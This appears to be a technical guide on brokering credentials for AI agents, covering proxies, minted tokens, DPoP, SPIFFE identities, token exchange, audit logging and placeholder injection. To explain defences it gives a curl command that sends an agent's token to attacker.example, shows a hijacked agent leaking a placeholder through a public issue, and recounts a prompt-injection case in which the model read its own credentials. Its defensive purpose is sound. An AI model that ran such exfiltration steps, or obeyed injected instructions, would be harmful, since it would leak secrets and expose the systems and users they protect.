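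DPoP works only if the issuer and the service both support it. An issuer that doesn't will return an ordinary bearer token, which the client can detect because the token is labeled "Bearer" instead of "DPoP". A service that doesn't support DPoP is harder to detect. Fett and colleagues expect that such a service would usually ignore the information about the key and accept the token as an ordinary bearer token. A thief could then use the token without a proof, and nothing would look wrong to the agent. A reviewer can test for this by sending the token from another machine without a proof. If the request succeeds, the token is a bearer token in practice.

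Even with full support, DPoP protects poorly against compromised agents. Fett and colleagues say its security is no longer guaranteed once an attacker can run code inside the client. If secure hardware holds the private key, the attacker can't copy the key but can still use it to sign requests. The attacker can also sign proofs dated in the future and take them away with the token, unless the service requires each proof to include an unpredictable value it recently supplied. In Hartman's scheme the agent creates the key pair itself, so without special hardware the private key probably sits in the same memory as the token. Hartman acknowledges that an attacker who takes both defeats the protection. DPoP would help most when only the token leaks, for instance through a log.

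### Whether to proxy or mint by default

Hartman recommends minting wherever the service supports it, mainly because proxying adds delay and a single point of failure. Posta, in *Credential Injection Patterns for AI Agents*, calls that recommendation "backward" for most enterprises today and argues for proxying. The article promotes a proxy gateway from Solo, so that side has a commercial interest, but readers can still judge the arguments on their merits.

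Hartman gives no measurements of the delay. An agent often waits several seconds for its language model between calls, so an extra hop inside the same data centre would rarely be noticeable. The delay could matter more when the agent downloads a very large repository or runs thousands of small database queries.

A minting broker can fail too, which weakens the single-point-of-failure argument for minting. Hartman requires the broker to stop issuing tokens if the decision point, the delivery point, the vault or the audit log is unavailable. With 60-second tokens, every agent would lose access within a minute. With one-hour tokens, some agents could continue for most of an hour, but a stolen token would also work for up to an hour. Minting therefore keeps agents running through an outage only for roughly the token's lifetime.

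Posta's main argument is that very few services check who is using a token. Posta says GitHub personal access tokens, API keys and the great majority of OAuth tokens for business software have no such check. API Evangelist's *DPoP* page also suggests this, since none of the providers in its catalogue declare support for the standard. Some may support it without declaring it, but support is clearly not common. Software that supports it does exist, and Spring's *OAuth 2.0 DPoP-bound Access Tokens*, for example, documents support in a widely used web framework.

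This narrows the dispute, because Hartman makes an exception for services that don't support DPoP. For those, the agent sends its proof to the proxy, which checks it and adds the real credential. If Posta is right that few services support DPoP, following Hartman's advice in full would also mean proxying most services. However, Hartman leaves DPoP out of the minimum version of the system, so a basic installation could give agents plain bearer tokens and still follow the draft.

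Posta also argues that many services, including GitHub, can't issue a suitable token on demand, while Hartman lists GitHub among the platforms that can. Both are right, because they mean different tokens. GitHub can issue a token to an app that acts as itself, which would suit the coding agent. A token to act as a particular employee requires that employee's consent in a browser, so the gateway has to obtain it once and store it. A newer mechanism called ID-JAG replaces the consent screen with a company-wide policy, but Posta points out that the company's login system and the service must both support it, and that the gateway still has to store the resulting token.

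More services may soon issue tokens directly to agents. *Workload Authorization Grant* (Carleton, Steele and colleagues, 2026) proposes that an administrator register an agent platform with a service once. The platform can then sign a grant naming any one of its agents, and the service exchanges the grant for an access token under its own rules. The sample grant lasts five minutes. Pogorelec (2026) reports in *Anthropic tests giving Claude agents their own credentials* that Anthropic supports the proposal in beta and that Datadog and PostHog accept these grants in their MCP servers. This weakens Posta's point about minting but not the one about theft, because the grant is itself a bearer credential. Carleton and colleagues list proof of possession as an open issue. Their proposal covers only agents acting as themselves, not on behalf of a user.

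In the gateway Posta describes, the agent's software sends the user's company login token with each call. The gateway stores service tokens by user, not by session, so a thief who copied Alice's login token and could reach the gateway might be able to use any service Alice had connected, until the login token expired or a rule blocked the request. Posta's claim that nothing on the agent's side is worth stealing is therefore too strong. A proxy still needs a narrow, short-lived way to identify the agent.

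Another option is to let the agent's software hold a token but keep it from the language model. *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization* (Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues, 2026), a draft by authors from AWS, OpenAI, Okta and other companies, takes roughly this position. It calls fixed API keys an "antipattern" and favours short-lived credentials, but forbids giving the model any access to them. This can work for an agent whose model only chooses from a fixed list of tools. But a coding agent's model also writes and runs programs, which could read the token if they run in the same environment as the agent's software.

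Anthropic had this problem in an earlier design that ran model-written code in the same container as credentials. According to its *Scaling Managed Agents*, a prompt injection only had to get the model to read its own environment. An attacker who got the tokens could then start new, unrestricted sessions and give them work. Anthropic considered narrower tokens but instead moved the tokens out of reach, because narrowing them relies on an assumption about "what Claude can't do with a limited token", which becomes less safe as models improve.

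This is a good argument against relying on narrow tokens alone, but it also applies to proxies. A rule that lets an agent open pull requests also depends on an assumption about what a clever model can do with them. The proxy adds control over each request. It can refuse the next one as soon as something looks wrong, and a thief can't use a copied service credential from another machine. With minting, the decision point approves a token request but can't monitor how the agent then uses the token. For an agent that might read a hostile bug report halfway through its work, this difference seems to be the best reason to prefer proxying.

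A builder can also combine the two by having the intermediary mint a short-lived token and add it to the request, so the agent never receives the token. Posta describes this arrangement in the open-source version of agentgateway. The proxy still adds delay, but a token that leaks between the intermediary and the service will soon expire. This is probably the best default where the service allows it.

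### Choosing by type of service

The intermediary has to support the service's protocol as well as its credentials. Databases and SSH servers don't use web requests, so a web proxy can't handle them. Some products do support them. Infisical, for example, advertises that its *Agent Vault*, still in preview, lets agents access both without giving them the credentials. The table assumes the builder will use a proxy where one is practical.

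| Type of service | What the agent holds | What the intermediary does | What to check |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tools that already go through the intermediary, such as connectors | Nothing | Adds the credential for the named tool | That the tool's output never includes the credential |
| Web service with a fixed API key | A placeholder if the software demands a key, otherwise nothing | Adds the real key | That the service rejects the placeholder |
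| Code host or cloud platform that can mint tokens | A placeholder or nothing | Mints a short-lived token and adds it to the request | That the token covers only the repository or resource the task needs |
| Service the agent uses on behalf of a person | A placeholder or nothing | Stores that person's token after they consent, then adds it | That one user's agent can't use another user's token |
| Service whose clients sign each request | A placeholder | Signs the request again with the real key | That the intermediary discards the original signature |
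| Database or SSH server | A placeholder or nothing if a suitable proxy exists, otherwise a short-lived login | Connects for the agent, or issues the login | Whether an open connection outlasts the login |
| Service with too much traffic for a proxy | A short-lived token, with DPoP if the service checks it | Mints the token | Whether the token works from another machine without a proof |
| Old service that takes only long-lived keys and can't go through a proxy | Preferably no access. If access is essential, a separate key for each task | Revokes the key after the task | That the service rejects the key afterwards |

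## Identifying the agent to the intermediary and to no one else

An agent that holds only a placeholder still has to identify itself, because the intermediary chooses both the rules and the real credential based on who is calling. A compromised agent, or a malicious package running beside it, can put any name in a simple header such as `X-Agent-Name: billing-fixer`. Kasselman and colleagues therefore require a credential that lets the recipient verify that the caller controls the name.

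Even a cryptographic signature may prove little about an agent's identity. In Sweeney's draft, each agent generates its own key pair when it starts, and the server must accept keys it has never seen before. Any program can generate such a key, so a signature shows only that the caller is the same one that used the key earlier. The agent can also state which language model it runs, but Sweeney warns that nobody verifies this and that the agent's credential stays valid if the operator swaps the model.

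Something other than the agent has to confirm the agent's identity to the intermediary. This could be the program that starts the agent, the platform it runs on or a private network it connects through. None of these can detect a hijack, because a hijacked agent keeps its identity. If malicious instructions in a bug report take over the billing agent, it still passes every identity check.

### Session tokens

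Hartman's proxying model relies on a session token, but the draft doesn't specify how the agent gets one. A workable arrangement for the coding agent would be:

1. Alice assigns a bug to the agent. The launcher, a trusted program that starts agents, asks the intermediary to open a run.
2. The intermediary generates a long random string and stores it with the agent's name, Alice's name, the repository and an expiry time.
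3. The launcher puts the string in the agent's environment.
4. The agent sends the string with each request, and the intermediary looks up the stored details.

The pull-request call then looks like this:

```
POST /repos/acme/billing/pulls HTTP/1.1
Host: intermediary.internal
Authorization: Bearer tok_PLACEHOLDER
X-Run-Token: run_7Hd3pL
```

The intermediary removes the session token and the placeholder before it forwards the request. If a client library can't send an extra header, the builder can use the session token as the placeholder. That saves work, but a placeholder that leaks into a log is then a working credential for the intermediary.

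Anyone who copies a session token and can reach the intermediary can act as that run until the token expires. Tying the token to a network path makes this much harder. For example, the intermediary can listen on a socket that exists only inside the agent's sandbox, or give each sandbox its own address and refuse the token from any other. Then, if a hijacked agent posts its token in a public comment, nobody outside the sandbox can use it.

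Malicious code inside the sandbox can still use both the token and the socket, but if each run has its own sandbox, that code can impersonate only one agent.

### Workload identity with SPIFFE and SPIRE

With a workload identity, nobody has to hand the agent a secret at the start. SPIFFE is an open standard for naming programs and proving their names, and SPIRE is software that implements it. SPIRE consists of a central server and a helper program on every machine. (SPIRE calls the helper an "agent", which is confusing here.) SPIFFE's *SPIRE Concepts* describes how a program gets its identity:

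1. An administrator registers the program's identity with the server, along with the properties a program must have to receive it. These might include its Unix user, its file path or the account it runs under in Kubernetes, which manages containers across many machines.
2. The helper proves which machine it is running on. On Amazon's cloud it sends an identity document, which the server checks with Amazon.
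3. The server sends the helper the registrations for that machine and signs the certificates, which the helper keeps ready.
4. The program connects to a local socket and asks for its identity, without presenting a password.
5. The helper asks the operating system which process is calling, looks up that process's properties and compares them with the registrations.
6. If they match, the program receives its certificate.

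The billing agent then connects to the intermediary over mutual TLS, in which both ends present certificates and prove that they hold the matching private keys. In Hartman's scheme, the identity also includes the user and the session, so it might be `spiffe://acme.example/agent/alice/run-7`. It lasts an hour by default, and the agent must repeat the checks to get another.

A thief who copies the certificate can't use it without the private key. With both, the thief can pose as the agent until the certificate expires, unless the intermediary also checks the network path. Kasselman and colleagues suggest keeping the key in secure hardware where possible, so that it can't leave the machine.

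SPIFFE identities also come as signed tokens, which are less secure than certificates. SPIFFE's *JWT SVID* acknowledges that they are bearer tokens, which a thief can replay. Each token names its intended recipient and has an expiry time, which the specification recommends keeping very short. SPIFFE advises using certificates whenever possible, but some network layouts rule them out. If a load balancer ends the encrypted connection and opens a new one, the intermediary receives the load balancer's certificate instead of the agent's. The agent can then sign each request with its own key, since the signature still reaches the intermediary. It is simpler to let the agent connect to the intermediary directly.

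The checks depend on how carefully the administrator wrote the registrations. Encryption Consulting, a security consultancy, warns that with loose rules any program on a verified machine can claim any identity registered there. Even with tight rules, a script that the agent downloads and executes may run as the same user and in the same container as the agent, in which case the helper would give it the same identity. Ganesan adds that most desktop operating systems can't reliably prove which process asked for a signature, and that workload identity is poorly suited to developers' laptops.

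Some sources also disagree about how finely to divide identities. Red Hat's *Wiring zero trust identity for AI agents* (2026) argues against a certificate for each user, because SPIRE is built for long-running programs that administrators register at deployment, while users come and go. Hartman divides identities even more finely, with one for each session, but doesn't explain who would create and delete all those registrations.

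### Agyn's certificate for each run

Agyn, an open-source platform for running agents on Kubernetes, automates this. When a new message arrives on a conversation thread, the platform creates a pod (a group of containers) for that user and task (Benkovich and Valkov, *Agyn*, 2026). It also requests a certificate for the pod from OpenZiti, software that builds a private network on top of the ordinary one.

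The agent can reach the platform's services only through this private network. OpenZiti checks the certificate as the connection opens, before any application code runs. A gateway then reads the agent's identity from the connection and passes it along, so every later service can identify the agent that made the request. Network rules restrict each agent to the services it needs. After the agent has been idle for a set time (five minutes by default), the platform stops the pod and deletes its identity.

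The network path is therefore part of the check, so a stolen session token or password is useless to someone who can't join the network. The certificate's private key is more useful to a thief because it admits its holder to the network. Benkovich and Valkov describe no check that ties the key to one pod, so a thief who copied it might be able to connect from elsewhere until the platform deleted the identity. In their design, a separate container in the pod handles the network traffic. Containers in a pod have separate file systems, so if the key stays in that container, code in the agent's container can use the connection but can't copy the key.

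Deleting the identity is a good defence against old copies, but the five-minute countdown starts only when activity stops. An active agent sends a signal every ten seconds, and a compromised agent could presumably keep sending it, so a builder who adopts this arrangement should also set a maximum lifetime for the identity.

Agyn suggests that giving each run its own identity is practical to automate. Benkovich and Valkov compare Agyn's features with those of four other platforms but report no attack tests, so how well it resists attacks is unknown. They also give no figures for how many identities it can manage at once.

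### Bringing the user into the decision

If an agent acts only for itself, the intermediary needs to identify only the agent. If the agent acts for Alice, the intermediary also has to identify her, so that it can apply her permissions and find her credential.

The intermediary can index stored service tokens by user and service. When an agent running for Alice sends a request to the code host, the intermediary retrieves Alice's token for that host. It must get Alice's name from the run's stored record or from a signed token, never from something the agent can edit, or a hijacked agent could ask for Bob's entry. Sweeney's draft puts an opaque handle for the stored credential inside a token that the server signs, so the agent can't change the handle to point to a different entry.

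When Alice's identity has to cross several systems, a standard called token exchange can carry it. Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, define a request that contains a subject token for the user and, optionally, an actor token for whoever is acting. The issuer checks both and returns a new token. For the billing agent, its main contents might be:

```
recipient (aud):   https://intermediary.internal
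subject (sub):     alice
actor (act):       billing-fixer/run-7
expires (exp):     60 seconds after issue
```

Jones and colleagues call this delegation, because the agent keeps its own identity while acting for Alice. Without the actor token, the exchange can still succeed, but the result is impersonation, in which the new token names only Alice and a recipient can't tell the agent from her.

The exchange also leaves Alice's original login token valid, so it should happen where the agent can't read that token. In Red Hat's demonstration, a proxy intercepts Alice's request before it reaches the service that runs the agents, and makes the exchange there. The issuer should also authenticate whoever requests the exchange. Jones and colleagues warn that otherwise anyone with a stolen token can exchange it for other tokens.

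At each step, Red Hat checks a certificate that shows which service is calling and a signed token that shows on whose behalf it is calling. A thief with only the token can't open the connection. But because the checks are independent, a compromised service with its own valid certificate might be able to present a token stolen from another service. The recipient can prevent this by checking that the caller and the token belong together.

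### The intersection of two sets of permissions

Once the intermediary knows both parties, it needs a rule for combining their permissions. Red Hat's *When an AI agent acts on your behalf* (2026) gives a simple one:

effective permissions = user's permissions ∩ agent's permissions

The agent can do only what both the user's permissions and its own allow. In Red Hat's example, Bob can read Finance and Admin documents, and an agent called `summarizer-tech` can read Finance and Engineering documents. When Bob uses the agent, it can read only Finance and public documents. Of the five documents in the demonstration, Bob can open three himself and two through the agent. Carol has access only to HR documents, so her permissions don't overlap with those of `summarizer-tech`. In the storage example in Red Hat's *The last mile* (2026), the gateway refuses a request when there is no overlap, before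 contacting Amazon for a credential.

The permissions come from a policy file and not from the agent's name, so an agent deployed as `summarizer-everything` starts with no access.

The rule reduces access only if somebody has narrowed the agent's list. Alice and `summarizer-tech` both have access to just Engineering and Finance, so using the agent doesn't narrow her departmental access. Another agent in the demonstration, `reviewer-general`, has access to every department, so it never narrows anyone's. The billing agent's useful restriction is its own list, which limits it to one repository however many Alice can open.

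Amazon's storage service can enforce the intersection itself. The gateway requests a temporary credential and attaches a policy, and Amazon allows only what both the policy and the underlying role permit. Red Hat presents this as protection against bugs in the gateway, but the protection is only partial because the gateway writes the policy. If the gateway calculated the intersection wrongly, only the role would limit access.

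Red Hat also refuses any request not made on behalf of a user. That is a sensible default for assistants, but it rules out an agent that updates dependencies every night. Such an agent needs its own narrow permissions and a named owner. Running it under the account of whoever set it up would give it that person's access and put a misleading name in the records.

Red Hat says its tokens follow the pattern in the standard by Jones and colleagues, but it reverses the order, making the agent the subject and the user the actor. When Alice's agent passes work to a second agent, Alice's name moves one level deeper, among the prior actors. Under the standard, a recipient must ignore prior actors when deciding access. Red Hat's demonstration works because its own policy engine reads every level, but a service that followed the standard would not apply the limits on Alice's access.

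The record of who handed work to whom can also be false. *Delegation Chain Splicing in OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange (RFC 8693)*, which Sweeney dates to February 2026, points out that the nested names have no separate signatures and that an attacker with two or more genuine tokens could combine parts of them into a chain that never happened. Sweeney proposes a signed receipt for every handover. A builder with a single intermediary can avoid most of the problem by opening a new run for each agent and recording its parent.

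### What the service sees

This identification goes no further than the intermediary. The code host receives an ordinary request with an ordinary credential, and its records show the account that owns that credential.

If the intermediary uses Alice's token, the code host records that Alice opened the pull request, so her own work and the work of all her agents look the same. If it uses an app's token, the records name the app instead of Alice. Alice might then be able to approve a pull request that her agent opened, even if the code host stops authors from approving their own.

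Ganesan also found this loss of attribution in past incidents. It happens even without an intermediary, when an agent holds Alice's token directly. An intermediary can at least record which agent made each request.

Kasselman and colleagues set out minimum contents for an audit record, and Hartman gives a sample entry. Neither is quite enough to trace a pull request back to a run. Hartman's entry names the service and the action but has no separate field for the resource, so it would show a message to Slack without the channel. An investigator would need the original request form, of which the entry holds only a hash. A useful entry for the billing agent would combine the two lists and add the account used and the service's reply:

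| Field | Example | Why it matters |
|---|---|---|
| Time | 09:46:40 UTC | Orders events |
| Agent and run | `billing-fixer`, `run-7` | Separates runs of the same agent |
| User or owner | Alice | Shows on whose behalf the agent acted |
| Service and account | Code host, Acme app | Links the entry to the account in the service's records |
| Credential reference | `vault-item-31` | Shows what to revoke, without storing the secret |
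| Action and resource | Open pull request, `acme/billing` | Shows what the agent asked for |
| Decision and rule | Allowed, rule 12, version 4 | Explains why the request passed |
| Approver and risk signals | None | Shows whether a person or a warning affected the decision |
| Service's reply | Created, pull request 91 | Matches the entry to one event at the service |
| Correlation ID | `c-5520` | Connects related requests, approvals and revocations |

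Without the service's reply in the log, an investigator has to match the two sets of records by time, which fails when two agents use the same account in the same second. The intermediary should also log refused requests, since a run of refusals may be the earliest evidence of a hijack.

The log must also be hard to alter. Hartman includes a hash of earlier entries in each new one, so that later edits can be detected, and prevents both the decision point and the delivery point from changing or deleting entries.

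With minting, the log would stop at the issue of the token, because the agent then calls the service directly.

### The case for agent identities that services can see

An internal log helps only people who can read it. If the billing agent starts filing abusive reports in other people's repositories, the code host sees them as coming from Alice or the Acme app and can block only that account. It can't suspend one agent, set stricter limits for agents, or check the intermediary's version of events. This is a strong argument for letting services recognise agents directly.

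Kasselman and colleagues propose doing so with existing standards. The access token names the agent as the client and the user as the subject, and the service must consider both when deciding whether to grant access. An IETF working group has adopted their draft, which continues under a new name.

Ganesan's design goes further by using a hardware-held key for each agent and service. The service stores each public key as a separate credential linked to Alice's account, so Alice or the service can revoke one agent without affecting anything else. Alice also uses her passkey to sign a "mandate" that lists the permitted services, actions and expiry. Each signed request includes a fingerprint of the latest entry in the agent's action log, so services hold their own evidence if someone later rewrites the log. Services can't get this evidence from an intermediary's private log.

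The main obstacle is adoption. McGuinness (2026), in *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation*, finds that existing specifications don't consistently define how to represent an agent acting for a user across different kinds of token. Two services could both claim to support delegation and still interpret the same token differently. Ganesan's design also requires each service to store new keys and check mandates, or to accept them through a company login system. Ganesan notes a privacy risk too, because services could use evidence from secure hardware to link an agent's activity across them.

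Recognition by the service also does little to stop a hijacked agent, whose requests would still carry a valid signature.

The two positions are more compatible than they look, because a service can recognise an agent that doesn't hold the credential. The intermediary can keep a separate app account for each important agent, so the code host can show each one under its own name and limit or revoke its access separately. Sweeney's draft proposes proxying requests to today's services and issuing tokens that name both the user and the agent once a service supports them. An operator who wants to keep proxying could have the intermediary present those tokens.

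For now, a private identity at the intermediary seems the right default, with separate accounts where the service's own records matter. Reasonable choices for common situations are:

| Situation | How the intermediary identifies the agent | What the service should see |
|---|---|---|
| Agent on a developer's laptop | A session token, accepted only from the agent's sandbox | The developer's account, or an app if the service offers one |
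| Short job in a disposable sandbox | A session token that expires with the job | An app account for that type of agent |
| Long-running agents on cloud machines | A SPIFFE certificate for each agent, plus a signed token for the user | The user's account where personal permissions matter |
| Many short runs that use internal services | A network certificate for each run | The agent's identity at internal services, an ordinary account elsewhere |
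| Scheduled agent with no user present | Any of these methods, with a named owner on record | Its own app account |
| Service that can read agent identities | Any of these methods | Both the agent and the user |

### Signs of failure

Most identification failures cause no errors, because requests continue to succeed. A reviewer has to look for them or provoke them:

- **Several agents share one identity.** The log shows overlapping runs under one name, or one run on two machines at once. Revoking the identity would stop them all, and nobody could tell which one had misbehaved.
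- **The intermediary trusts a name in the request.** Change the user or agent name in a header from inside the sandbox. If the intermediary uses a different credential or set of rules, a hijacked agent could do the same.
- **A copied session token works elsewhere.** Send it from another sandbox. If the request succeeds, the token isn't tied to its path.
- **An unrelated program can get the agent's identity.** Start one on the same machine under a different user and ask SPIRE for an identity. It should receive nothing, or only an identity of its own.
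- **An identity outlives its run.** Stop the agent, then repeat its last request with the same token or certificate.
- **The session token reaches the service.** Send a request through the intermediary to a test server that records what it receives, and search the record for the token.
- **Every entry names the same user.** The intermediary may be using the account of whoever installed it, in which case everyone's agents have that person's permissions.

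## Adding the real credential to the agent's request

Once the intermediary knows which agent is calling, it has to put a real credential into a request that the agent has already written and encrypted. Most products use a proxy outside the sandbox, which decrypts the request, replaces a placeholder with the credential and forwards the request to the service. Docker, Anthropic and OpenAI offer versions of this. *Building Managed Agents That Use GitHub Without Exposing Your Token* (2026) describes another for Google's Gemini agents, in which the placeholder is the word `dummy`.

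### One request from start to finish

Suppose the billing agent has fixed its bug and wants to open a pull request. The operator has replaced the old code-host token with `tok_R7/d4+mZ`, which only the intermediary holds. The launcher starts the sandbox with these settings:

```
CODEHOST_TOKEN=ph_codehost_6b1e09
HTTPS_PROXY=http://run_7Hd3pL@intermediary.internal:3128
```

The first is the placeholder. The second is the intermediary's address, with the session token in front of it.

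1. The agent's client library reads `CODEHOST_TOKEN` and writes the placeholder into the `Authorization` header, as it would with a real token.
2. `HTTPS_PROXY` makes the client connect to the intermediary instead of the code host. The client presents the session token and asks for a tunnel to `api.codehost.example`.
3. The client starts TLS, the encryption that HTTPS uses, through the tunnel. An ordinary proxy would pass the encrypted bytes along unread. The intermediary instead answers in the code host's place, with a certificate for `api.codehost.example` that it has signed itself. The sandbox trusts that signature, so the client sends its request and the intermediary can decrypt it.
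4. The intermediary checks that this credential may go to this host in this header, and that its rules allow the agent to open a pull request.
5. It replaces the placeholder with the real token.
6. It opens a second TLS connection, to the real code host, and checks the code host's certificate. The client can no longer do that, because it sees only the intermediary's certificate.
7. It searches the code host's response for the token, masks any copy it finds, encrypts the response for the client and sends it back.

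After decryption, the intermediary has this request:

```
POST /repos/acme/billing/pulls HTTP/1.1
Host: api.codehost.example
Authorization: Bearer ph_codehost_6b1e09
Content-Type: application/json

{"title": "Fix invoice rounding", "head": "fix-rounding", "base": "main"}
```

It sends this one to the code host:

```
POST /repos/acme/billing/pulls HTTP/1.1
Host: api.codehost.example
Authorization: Bearer tok_R7/d4+mZ
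Content-Type: application/json

{"title": "Fix invoice rounding", "head": "fix-rounding", "base": "main"}
```

Only the `Authorization` line has changed. Neither version contains the session token, because the client sent it earlier, when requesting the tunnel.

ZenML's tutorial *Credential proxy* demonstrates a simpler version. The agent runs `curl` against a private wiki without a token. The proxy logs that it added an `Authorization` header, and the wiki logs an authenticated request and a successful reply. The demonstration uses unencrypted HTTP between containers on one laptop, so it omits the two TLS connections.

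Some proxies choose the credential by the request's destination and ignore placeholders. For services that Docker Sandboxes supports directly, such as GitHub, the proxy overwrites the authentication header on any HTTPS request to the service's host. The cloud version does this even for credentials that the user defines, according to Docker's *Authenticate cloud agents*. This is simpler than matching a placeholder and not much less secure, because any program in the sandbox could have read the placeholder anyway. But if the user has two accounts on the same service, the proxy can no longer use the placeholder to choose between them.

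None of this helps if the real key is also in the agent's files. Docker's *Isolation layers* warns that the `.env` file in the user's repository is readable inside the sandbox, even in the mode that protects the repository from changes.

### Decrypting the agent's traffic

The intermediary has to decrypt the agent's request because it can't edit a header it can't read, as OpenFirma's *Inject credentials* explains. Docker describes this as a man-in-the-middle technique, the same one used in attacks, but here the operator has deliberately configured the sandbox to trust the intermediary's certificate authority, the key pair that signs its certificates. Anyone who obtained the private key could impersonate any website to the agent, so that key should stay outside the sandbox, and only the sandbox should trust the authority, not the developer's whole machine.

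Decryption also exposes source code and conversations with the model to the intermediary. *Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) describes an open-source system that limits this exposure. The system runs each job in a micro-VM, a small virtual machine with its own operating-system kernel. The machine has no network card, so all its traffic has to pass through a program on the host. Each machine gets its own certificate authority, which is valid only for sites that have a credential attached. The client would reject a certificate that this authority signed for any other site.

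By default, Tracekit Box leaves other HTTPS connections encrypted and reads only the host, port and server name. A hijacked agent could send its placeholder over one of these connections, but the recipient couldn't use it. The agent can't send the real token because the token isn't in the machine. This seems a better default than decrypting everything, although the intermediary can't check what the agent sends to those hosts.

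### Why the credential needs a fixed destination and header

Any program in the sandbox can read the placeholder, so a hijacked agent could try this:

```
curl https://attacker.example/ -H "Authorization: Bearer $CODEHOST_TOKEN"
```

If the intermediary replaced the placeholder in every request, it would deliver the real token to the attacker. It therefore has to tie each credential to a destination, here `api.codehost.example`, and replace the placeholder only in requests sent there.

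The right destination is not enough on its own, because strangers can read what the agent posts on the code host. The agent could open an issue in a public repository and use the placeholder as the text:

```
POST /repos/stranger/notes/issues HTTP/1.1
Host: api.codehost.example
Authorization: Bearer ph_codehost_6b1e09
Content-Type: application/json

{"title": "hello", "body": "ph_codehost_6b1e09"}
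```

If the intermediary replaced both copies, it would publish the real token in the issue. If it replaces only the one in the `Authorization` header, the issue contains a harmless string. The agent can still post the issue unless the rules on permitted actions forbid it.

Docker's *Manage credentials* describes both limits. For a custom secret (one for a service that Docker doesn't support directly), the user lists the hosts and can name the headers. The proxy makes the replacement only over HTTPS, for those hosts and in those headers. If the user names no header, Docker uses a default list. Docker stopped replacing custom secrets that had no destination hosts in version 0.51.0, released on 3 November 2026.

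Docker also lets users install "kits", which are packages that configure an agent. A kit can request credentials and specify the domains that will receive them. Unless the kit came with Docker Sandboxes, the user has to approve each credential and its domains. In an unattended run nobody can approve the request, so the sandbox starts without the credential.

Tracekit Box is stricter. It ties a secret to exact host names and one header. If the placeholder appears anywhere else in traffic the proxy reads, the proxy blocks the request and records the attempt. The record is useful evidence because a legitimate program has little reason to put its access token in the text of an issue.

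| System | Allowed destinations | Where it inserts the secret | Placeholder found elsewhere |
|---|---|---|---|
| Docker Sandboxes (local custom secrets) | Listed hosts, wildcards allowed | Chosen headers, or a default list | Goes out unchanged |
| Tracekit Box | Exact hosts | One header | Blocked where the proxy can read it |
| Anthropic vaults (environment variables) | Listed hosts, wildcards allowed, or any host the network rules permit | Headers, body or both | Goes out unchanged |

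Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* recommends limiting which hosts can receive the secret. It also notes that putting the secret in the request body is riskier than putting it in the headers, because agents often assemble the body from the material they are working on. By default, both locations are allowed. According to Anthropic's *Credentials*, the "unrestricted" host setting leaves the sandbox's network rules as the only limit on where the secret can go. Builders should set both the allowed hosts and the location explicitly.

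Wildcards also need care because some providers give every customer a subdomain, so `*.provider.example` could include one that belongs to an attacker. OpenAI accepts only exact host names for secrets in its hosted sandboxes. It also keeps separate lists for the hosts the sandbox can contact and the hosts that can receive a secret, which is useful because an agent may need to download packages from a site that should never receive its code-host token.

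Checking the host is difficult because it can appear in several places in one request: the tunnel request, the TLS handshake, the `Host` header and sometimes the first line of the request itself. Ghosh found a serious bug of this kind by fuzzing, or feeding a program many malformed inputs. An agent could open a tunnel to an approved host and then send a request whose first line gave a full address at another site. The proxy's check missed the second address, so it added the real secret. If the approved host forwarded requests according to that first line, it could have passed the credential to the other site, while the log showed only the approved host. Ghosh has fixed the bug, but other proxies could easily contain a similar one.

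All 13 of Tracekit Box's end-to-end checks passed on 26 October 2026. In one, the proxy replaced a placeholder in the `Authorization` header with the real credential, which a test server received. In another, the proxy refused the same placeholder in a header called `X-Smuggle`. These checks were scripted, and Ghosh has not yet tested the box with a capable agent instructed to escape.

### When the service sends the secret back

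Even a credential sent only to the approved host can get back to the agent in the host's response. Docker gives the example of an error message that repeats the request's headers. Debugging pages that show visitors their own request do the same. A hijacked agent could look for such a page on the approved host, send it an ordinary request and read the real credential in the response.

When Docker's proxy has inserted a custom secret, it therefore searches the response's headers and body before passing them on. It recognises four forms of the secret. For the token in this example, they would be:

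| Form | What the response would contain |
|---|---|
| Original | `tok_R7/d4+mZ` |
| JSON-escaped | `tok_R7\/d4+mZ` |
| Percent-encoded, as in web addresses | `tok_R7%2Fd4%2BmZ` |
| Base64, a common way to write data as plain text | `dG9rX1I3L2Q0K21a` |

Docker warns that this filtering "cannot guarantee that a secret stays hidden". The filter doesn't inspect WebSocket messages, and it can't recognise every way a service might transform a secret. For example, a service could split the secret between two fields, and neither half would match.

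Base64 encodes three bytes at a time, so the encoded form of the token depends on what comes before it. If a page encodes the whole header value, `Bearer tok_R7/d4+mZ`, the result is `QmVhcmVyIHRva19SNy9kNCttWg==`, which does not contain the string in the table's last row. A filter has to search for the token in all three possible alignments, and Docker doesn't say whether its filter does.

Docker describes this filtering only for custom secrets, so a builder who uses the built-in GitHub service shouldn't assume that it also covers the GitHub token.

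Tracekit Box also masks hexadecimal copies of the secret. It asks approved services for uncompressed responses so that it can read them, and it refuses partial responses. Docker returns an error for partial responses and for compression it can't read. Refusing partial responses is sensible, since an agent that could request any range of bytes could collect the secret a few characters at a time.

Masking secrets in responses is easy to get wrong. Ghosh found three bugs by fuzzing the proxy and has fixed them all. In the first, the proxy didn't mask the response body if the status code was below 100. In the second, the text that replaced a secret could combine with the characters around it to form the secret again. In the third, parts of a secret stayed visible if that secret contained another one and the response arrived in pieces.

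dvergr's *Boundary secret injection*, the documentation of an agent library written in Clojure, calls a single pass of masking "complete" because the agent never holds the original. That is true only if the service returns the value in a form the filter knows. Masking is a useful second defence against careless services, but the main one is to send secrets only to hosts that don't repeat them. Against a malicious service masking achieves little, as the service already has the token.

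### Ways to avoid decrypting HTTPS

**A changed base address.** A setting such as `CODEHOST_URL`, shown earlier, can point the client at the intermediary. The client then connects to the intermediary directly, so the intermediary doesn't have to forge a certificate. terok, a program that launches coding agents, edits the agents' configuration files to do this. It points one tool at a web address and GitHub's command-line tool at a local socket, and writes no secrets into the files. OpenShell, NVIDIA's sandbox for agents, does something similar for model calls. The agent calls `https://inference.local`, and a router removes any credential the agent supplied, adds the real one and forwards the call.

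This is probably the best choice for a single well-behaved client, such as the one that calls the language model. It works less well for a coding agent that installs and writes programs, because each program needs its own setting. A service's replies can also contain full links to its real address, such as a link to the next page of results, and a client that follows one will bypass the intermediary.

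A **tool proxy** works like the connectors described earlier. The agent names an operation, such as `open_pull_request`, and a program outside the sandbox builds the whole request. This makes it easier to limit the agent to a few operations, but existing command-line programs can't use the proxy without changes.

The launcher can clone a Git repository before the agent starts and set up its remote, the stored address Git uses to fetch and push code, so that `git push` works without a login. If the remote points to a proxy that adds the token outside the sandbox, the agent can push without having access to the token. This protection is lost if the launcher instead writes the token into `.git/config`, where the agent can read it.

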